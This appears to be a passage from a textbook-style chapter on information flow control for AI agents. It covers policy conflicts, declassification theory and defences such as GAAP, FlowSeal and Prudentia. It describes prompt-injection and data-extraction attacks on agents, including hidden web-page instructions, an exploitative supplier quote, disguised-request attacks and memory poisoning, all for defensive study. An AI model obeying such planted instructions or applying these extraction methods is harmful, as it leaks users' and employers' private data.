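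The worst-case rule has an advantage over the finer methods because it keeps the clinic's label on the email whether the letter appears as a quotation, a paraphrase or a pattern in the punctuation. A mask also prevents the model from secretly encoding the passage it covers, except for the passage's length and position. A tracker that removes the label because it detects no trace of the letter doesn't protect against hidden encoding.

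The practical way to limit hidden information in Maya's email is to limit the assistant's freedom. If ordinary software inserts one of five weekdays into a fixed message, the assistant can't choose the greeting or word order. If the assistant writes the whole email, the supplier gets a more natural message, but nobody can be sure that it conveys only the day.

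## Deciding what may leave when policies disagree

Once Maya's assistant writes a message and the software works out the message's labels, the guard must send the message or stop it. Four policies may apply, covering confidentiality, integrity, privacy norms and harm, and they can conflict.

### Four messages and their verdicts

Suppose the assistant has drafted four messages:

- Maya asked it to offer the supplier a time, and it proposes Wednesday at ten.
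- Hidden text on the venue's web page told it to send the supplier her employer's discount limit.
- Maya asked it to forward her clinic letter to her employer as evidence for sick leave.
- Maya asked it to tell the supplier how to get the most gas from two cleaning products that react with each other, and it drew the answer from public sources.

We assume that the software tracks labels separately, so each message carries only the labels of the data behind it, and that the clinic counts as a trusted writer.

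| Message | Confidentiality | Integrity | Privacy norm | Harm |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Meeting time to the supplier | block: the day comes from the letter | allow | allow | allow |
| Discount limit to the supplier | block: the supplier is not a reader | block: the web page prompted it | none applies | allow |
| Clinic letter to the employer | block: the employer is not a reader | allow | allow: Maya chose to send it | allow |
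| Chemical answer to the supplier | allow | allow | none applies | block |

Most people would send the first and third messages and stop the other two. The confidentiality policy gets three of the four wrong, since it stops both messages that should be sent and allows the chemical answer. A majority vote does better, but it would still allow the chemical answer by two votes to one.

Weighted votes would not solve the problem, because the verdicts have no common scale. The confidentiality verdict comes from comparing the recipients with the permitted readers, and it is the same whether an unpermitted recipient is a harmless colleague or the employer's main competitor. The integrity verdict depends on what caused the action, and the privacy verdict depends on whether a combination of five parameters fits the norm. A harm classifier typically estimates a probability. Someone could convert all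 four into expected harm, but the harm falls on different people. A leaked discount limit costs the employer money, an unsent email loses Maya time, and a poisoning injures a stranger. Neither Maya nor her employer has the authority to decide how much risk to the stranger a convenient email justifies.

"Allow" also has two meanings in the table. The harm policy allows the discount limit to be released only in the sense that it does not forbid it. Maya's decision to forward her letter is positive permission from the person it is about. A guard that treats the absence of a prohibition as permission will release secrets merely because disclosing them is harmless.

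### Vetoes and rankings

The simplest way to combine the policies is to stop a message if any policy forbids it. In the table, this rule stops all four messages. Adding policies can only increase the number of messages stopped, including good ones. If four checks each wrongly stop 5% of good messages, and their errors are independent, together they stop 1 − 0.95⁴ ≈ 19% of good messages.

Kolluri and colleagues use a softer veto, which lets an outgoing call through if it passes either the confidentiality check or the integrity check. With a separate veto for harm, this rule would give the sensible answer in all four rows, but it would still release a secret that the assistant attached by mistake.

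Vetoes also cannot express a duty to disclose. Suppose a worker in the supplier's warehouse breathes in fumes from a leaking drum, and the supplier writes to ask what was in it. Maya's employer has one rule that product formulas never leave the company and another that anyone treating an exposure must get the ingredients at once. Sending nothing satisfies every veto but breaks the second rule.

A ranking would settle that conflict, but either order causes problems. If secrecy ranks higher, the doctor has to wait, and if disclosure ranks higher, a competitor can get the formula by inventing an accident. A ranking also ignores how much is at stake, because it treats even a trivial breach of the higher rule as worse than a grave breach of the lower one.

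### Exceptions written in advance

The employer could instead write an exception for this case. For example, the policy could keep formulas inside the company but let the safety officer give the ingredients to a clinic after calling it back on a published number. The exception specifies the condition, the person who decides and the recipient, so a false story in an email is not enough to get the ingredients released. But someone has to foresee the case, and the guard has to apply the two rules together correctly.

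*SafePyramid* (Zhang, He and colleagues, 2026) tests whether language models can do this. It pairs each of 1,000 conversations between a user and a chatbot with three policies of increasing difficulty. The first policy has about 16 independent rules. The second adds exceptions, which can excuse a breach of another rule, and conditional rules, which can turn acceptable behaviour into a breach. The third expresses a similar structure in invented terms, so a model cannot rely on familiar ideas of safety. The model being tested must list exactly the rules that the chatbot broke.

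The table gives the percentage of lists that were exactly right. In the one-rule-at-a-time version, the software first gathers the parts of the policy relevant to each rule, and the guard then judges each rule separately.

| Guard | Independent rules | With exceptions and conditions | In invented terms |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.5, whole policy | 54.0 | 35.3 | 12.9 |
| GPT-5.5, one rule at a time | 47.8 | 51.5 | 12.1 |
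| GPT-OSS-Safeguard-120B, whole policy | 38.6 | 2.0 | 0.2 |
| GPT-OSS-Safeguard-120B, one rule at a time | 46.5 | 42.3 | 8.0 |

OpenAI built the model GPT-OSS-Safeguard to apply policies that users supply. It almost never produced a correct list when the rules depended on each other, but it regained most of the lost accuracy when it checked the rules one at a time. This suggests that ordinary software should record which exceptions belong to which rule, and that the model should check only whether each condition holds. This requires a separate model call for each rule.

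These scores are strict, because a typical conversation breaks about six rules and a single mistake makes the whole list count as wrong. Language models also wrote the conversations, the policies and the reference answers, although human experts agreed with more than 90% of the answers they reviewed. The kind of mistake is more worrying than the exact rate, because on the second set of policies, models often applied an exception when one phrase resembled its condition and missed other details showing that it did not apply. In the warehouse case, a guard that makes this mistake might release the formula because an email contains the word "exposure".

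A guard may also have to find the right policy before applying it. In *RePolicy*, Jiang, Zhang and colleagues (2026) trained a small model to pick policies from a library and then judge an agent's actions. Reinforcement learning raised the share of cases in which the model's selection included the right policy from about 94.4% to 98.5%. The number of policies it picked per case also rose, from about 1.9 to 3.2, which makes it easier to include the right one. Each training case has one reference policy and one verdict, safe or unsafe, whereas Maya's messages fall under several policies at once. Choosing the right policies would not settle a conflict between them.

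### A verdict that depends on earlier reading

Under some policies, whether a reader may access a file depends on what that reader has already seen. Brewer and Nash described one in *The Chinese Wall Security Policy* (1989). The policy comes from finance, where an analyst who has inside knowledge of one company must not advise its competitor.

The policy groups files by company and places competing companies in the same conflict-of-interest class. An analyst may open a file in either of two cases:

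- The analyst has already opened a file about that company.
- The analyst has not opened a file about any company in that class.

A new analyst can therefore start with any company. After reading about Oil Company A, the analyst may still read about Bank A, which is in another class, but not about Oil Company B. If the analyst had started with Oil Company B, the policy would forbid Oil Company A instead, even though the files and their labels would be the same, because the policy depends on what the analyst has already read.

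Maya's employer might need this rule if two rival suppliers sent it confidential cost figures after it promised each of them that nobody who had seen the other's figures would negotiate with them. Her assistant could open either file first, but could not then open the other.

Brewer and Nash argue that the Bell-LaPadula model cannot express this policy. An administrator could clear each analyst in advance for at most one company in each class, but the analysts would lose their free choice. If the administrator cleared everyone for everything, nothing would stop an analyst from reading the files of two rivals. The model also keeps no record of what people have read, so a manager couldn't tell whether an analyst may cover for a sick colleague. This argument applies to clearances fixed in advance. A label that grows with each reading, like the one on an agent's context window, does keep the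 necessary history, and the software could refuse any reading that would put two rivals in the same label.

A second rule lets people write to a company's file only if they cannot read confidential data about any other company. Without it, an analyst who can read about Oil Company A and Bank A might copy Oil Company A's secrets into the bank's file, where a colleague who works on Oil Company B could read them. Under this rule, an analyst who has opened files on two companies can write to neither. This is as restrictive as label creep, although Brewer and Nash let data circulate freely once someone has disguised which company it concerns.

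An agent can remove the first supplier's figures by clearing its context window, provided it saved no notes about them. This doesn't get around the wall, because Brewer and Nash apply the rule to the human user, not to each program. Otherwise, a user could read both rivals' files through two programs. If two clean copies of the assistant each handle one rival and both report to Maya, she ends up with both sets of figures. The employer would need a separate negotiator for each rival, just as Brewer and Nash prove that a firm needs at least as many analysts as there are companies in its largest class.

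### Checks that must read the secret

A harm classifier has to read a message to judge it. If the classifier runs on another company's computers, checking an email that quotes Maya's clinic letter discloses the letter to that company before the guard has decided anything. The confidentiality policy must therefore allow the classifier to read the letter before the guard can apply the harm policy. If it doesn't, and every policy has a veto, the assistant can't send the letter even to Maya's own doctor.

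*An AI Agent Execution Environment to Safeguard User Data* (Stanley, Verma and colleagues, 2026) treats AI models as possible recipients in this way. Its system, GAAP, treats the company that runs a model as an outside party and asks the user before sending it private data. Under this rule, a harm check by a new company would need Maya's permission. The company that already runs the assistant's model could do the check, for example with a probe, without giving anyone else access to the data. An employer could also run a classifier on its own machines.

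A visible refusal can leak a secret, so GAAP restricts the error from a blocked call in the same way as the data that caused the block. The agent can react to the error, but the software controls any later message that depends on it.

### Who may authorise a release

An attacker should not be able to influence declassification. Robust declassification, the property that prevents this, requires that an attacker who interferes with a program learn no more than one who only watches.

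Kanniwadi and Myers (2026), in *Demystifying Information Flow Downgrading using the Real-Ideal Paradigm*, give a one-line example of a program that fails:

p := u × s

The attacker can see p and change u, but cannot see the secret s. If u starts at zero, an attacker who only watches sees zero and learns nothing, but one who sets u to 1 sees the secret. The hidden instruction on the web page in Maya's case has the same effect, because it makes the assistant send the discount limit it would otherwise have kept secret. Kolluri and colleagues aim to prevent this with a rule that allows an otherwise forbidden flow only when trusted data alone led to the decision.

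Robust declassification does not cover every way an attacker can use a secret. *Nonmalleable Information Flow Control*, by Cecchetti, Myers and Arden (2017), gives the example of a sealed-bid auction. Alice sends her bid to an auctioneer whom both bidders trust. Bob can't read her bid, but the system lets him submit a bid defined as hers plus one. The auctioneer endorses both bids as genuine and then announces them. Bob wins by the smallest possible margin without seeing Alice's bid beforehand.

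An agent makes this trick easy because an attacker can write the formula in ordinary language. Suppose two suppliers send confidential quotes to Maya's assistant, and the second writes, "Our price is one pound below your lowest other offer." The assistant has both quotes in its context window and fills in the number. If Maya's company accepts that number as the second supplier's bid, the supplier has used a figure it was never allowed to read.

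Cecchetti and colleagues' transparent endorsement rule would forbid the endorsement. Under this rule, a system may raise its trust in data only if whoever supplied the data could have read everything in it. The second supplier could not have read its rival's quote, so the assistant must not treat the calculated figure as a valid bid. Nonmalleable information flow limits both exceptions, declassification and endorsement, so that attackers can't exploit them by manipulating data they cannot read.

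The two protections have to work together because each kind of exception can enable the other. *A Calculus for Flow-Limited Authorization* (2021) proves a form of robust declassification that still lets a program release a low-integrity secret input. An attacker allowed to influence that input can then affect how much the release reveals.

Kanniwadi and Myers define all these properties by comparing attackers. Let A be a real attacker and B a weaker one. A program P has the property if

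for every A there is a B such that ⟦P | A⟧ ≈ ⟦P | B⟧.

The brackets stand for the program's trusted outputs together with whatever the attacker reveals of what it has learned. If the two sides match, the real attacker's extra powers gained it nothing. The properties differ only in how weak B must be:

| Property | Can B read public data? | What can B do to untrusted data? |
|---|---|---|
| Noninterference | no | nothing |
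| Robust declassification | yes | nothing |
| Transparent endorsement | no | insert values of its own |
| Nonmalleable information flow | yes | insert values of its own |

A real attacker can also change untrusted data using a formula that depends on secrets, as Bob does. No B in the table can do that. The auction fails the last test because an attacker who must choose a number without using Alice's bid cannot always bid exactly one more than she does.

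Kanniwadi and Myers also prove that, in programs that pass their type checker, an attacker can achieve nothing beyond what a weaker attacker could achieve at the declassification and endorsement steps, so a reviewer can concentrate on those steps. This would suit agents that write a complete plan before reading outside data, if the plan were in a language such a checker could handle. It would not help with free text from a model that has read both quotes. These properties limit only who can influence a release, so Maya could still approve a foolish one.

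*Securing LLM-Agent Long-Term Memory Against Poisoning* (Louck, 2026) applies nonmalleable flow to the notes that agents save. A note from an untrusted source may determine a payment or another consequential action only if two independent trusted sources, such as a company register and a bank, confirm the value, or if the user authorises that exact action. The authorisation names the tool, the value and the amount, and works only once, so an attacker cannot reuse it to pay someone else.

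In Louck's tests on eight models, attacks that disguised where a note came from succeeded up to 68% of the time against other defences and never against this one. Its guarantee assumes that the software labels each note's origin correctly. The defence also suits endorsement better than declassification. Two trusted sources can confirm that an account number is correct, but their agreement doesn't give the supplier a right to see the clinic letter.

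### Asking the owner

As in the decentralized label model, each owner can release only their own data, so Maya can release the meeting time and the clinic letter, and her employer can release the discount limit. Neither can waive a harm policy that belongs to the model's developer.

*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* presents FlowSeal, a system that asks the owner for consent. Each protected record carries its owner's name, and software outside the agent intercepts every outgoing call. It allows messages to recipients the owner trusts and refuses those to recipients on a block list. For anyone else, a separate model compares the message with the protected records and returns one word, SAFE or BLOCKED. To share a protected record, the agent can ask the software to get the owner's consent.

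The separate model decides only whether the message reveals anything derived from the records, not whether the disclosure would be acceptable. It should therefore block "Wednesday at ten", which depends on the clinic letter, and let Maya decide whether to release it. FlowSeal's proof of confidentiality holds unless this model wrongly answers SAFE.

The tests used three attacks that disguise a request for private data. In the first, the attacker invites the agent to fill in its part of a shared document. In the second, the attacker asks it to tidy a list of true and false statements about someone, then learns which are true from the entries it leaves. The third splits the task between an email and a shared page. The table gives the percentage of sensitive items that leaked with DeepSeek-V3.2 as the agent. The baseline is a detailed prompt that tells the agent to check identities and get consent.

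| Attack | Prompt only | FlowSeal |
|---|---|---|
| Shared document | 52.2 | 0.5 |
| List to tidy | 75.6 | 2.3 |
| Split between channels | 43.8 | 2.2 |

These large reductions depend on the separate model. When the researchers replaced it with a rule that passed every message, 24.9% of items leaked through the shared document. With a rule that blocked every message to unknown recipients, the agent completed none of the ordinary tasks.

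With the full system, the agent completed 72.4% of ordinary tasks, close to the best competing defence, but those tasks required no private data. In another test, where the request was legitimate and the owner would consent if asked, FlowSeal's agent delivered only 32.7% of the private items, against 61% to 86% for four other defences. It asked for consent less often, so many proper disclosures never happened. The researchers describe this as caution, but it would be a serious fault for Maya because two of her four messages need this kind of release.

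### Remembering the answer

Each GAAP permission allows or denies sending one item of private data to one outside party, and the software saves that decision for later tasks. It also logs disclosures. If the assistant gives an airline Maya's passport number and later downloads a booking confirmation, GAAP treats the confirmation as something that may contain the number and checks whether the friend may receive the number before the confirmation is forwarded to them.

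Stanley and colleagues tested GAAP with seven attacks on each of 20 tasks, and none of the attacks obtained private data without permission. Two defences that relied on a language model's judgement each let five of the seven attacks succeed on some tasks. GAAP protects only confidentiality, not integrity.

Saved permissions reduced the number of questions from 3.8 to 1.5 per task over 100 tasks, and from 57 to 7 for one early task. But 80 of the 100 tasks were variations on the other 20, so the same data and recipients came up often. Someone with more varied errands would probably answer more questions. Tasks took 188 seconds on average with protection and 28 without it, and protection made the two main benchmarks 2.9 times as expensive to run.

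The permission GAAP would request is too broad for Maya's email. The day comes from the clinic letter, so GAAP would prompt her to decide whether the letter's contents may go to the supplier. If she says yes and the software saves her answer, a later email could include her diagnosis without another prompt. She can allow the disclosure just once, but she has to notice the danger first. A safer permission would state a purpose and cover only the meeting time or an answer from a fixed list of weekdays.

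### The cost of approvals

If an agent asked about every action, it would be safe only as long as people read the questions. Kolluri and colleagues therefore measure how often a defence needs a person. For each task i, let vᵢ be the number of tool calls that fail the policy check and so need approval. They use two measures:

- The approval load is the sum of vᵢ over the tasks that the agent completes.
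- TCR@k is the share of all tasks that the agent completes with vᵢ ≤ k.

TCR@0 is therefore the share of tasks that the agent finishes with no approvals. The table gives results for OpenAI's o3-mini on AgentDojo's 97 tasks, averaged over five runs. The basic agent asks for approval before every consequential call. The others ask only when a call fails a policy check.

| Agent | Approval load | TCR@0 |
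|---|---|---|
| Basic | 48.2 | 24.3% |
| Basic with labels | 32.4 | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 18.8 | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | about 17 | 59.1% |

Labels alone removed a third of the approvals without reducing the number of completed tasks. Tests of task completion tend to miss this benefit because they compare a protected agent that isn't allowed to ask for approval with an unprotected one that doesn't need it. With o4-mini, Prudentia completed 73.2% of tasks with a load of 19.2, or about one approval for every four completed tasks. FIDES completed slightly more tasks, 75.7%, but needed nearly twice as many approvals.

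No people took part in these tests. Kolluri and colleagues counted the calls that would have needed approval and assumed a person would grant it whenever the task succeeded. They left out failed tasks, in which agents often repeated forbidden calls and a real user might have faced many approval requests. The figures therefore measure how often an agent would interrupt someone during successful tasks, but not whether that person would catch an attack.

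Prudentia lets the user endorse a whole document but deliberately offers no way to declassify one. Kolluri and colleagues reason that whether private data may leave depends on the situation, so the user should approve each outgoing call separately. The user has to answer more questions, but this avoids saving a broad permission that could expose Maya's diagnosis.

The wording of the question also affects whether she can answer it sensibly. If GAAP has descriptions of what each tool does, it can ask about sharing one file with one address. Otherwise, it might ask whether to share everything in the file system with everyone the email server can reach. For Maya's errand, a good question would include the exact message, "Wednesday at ten", the supplier's name, and the fact that the choice of day depends on her clinic letter.
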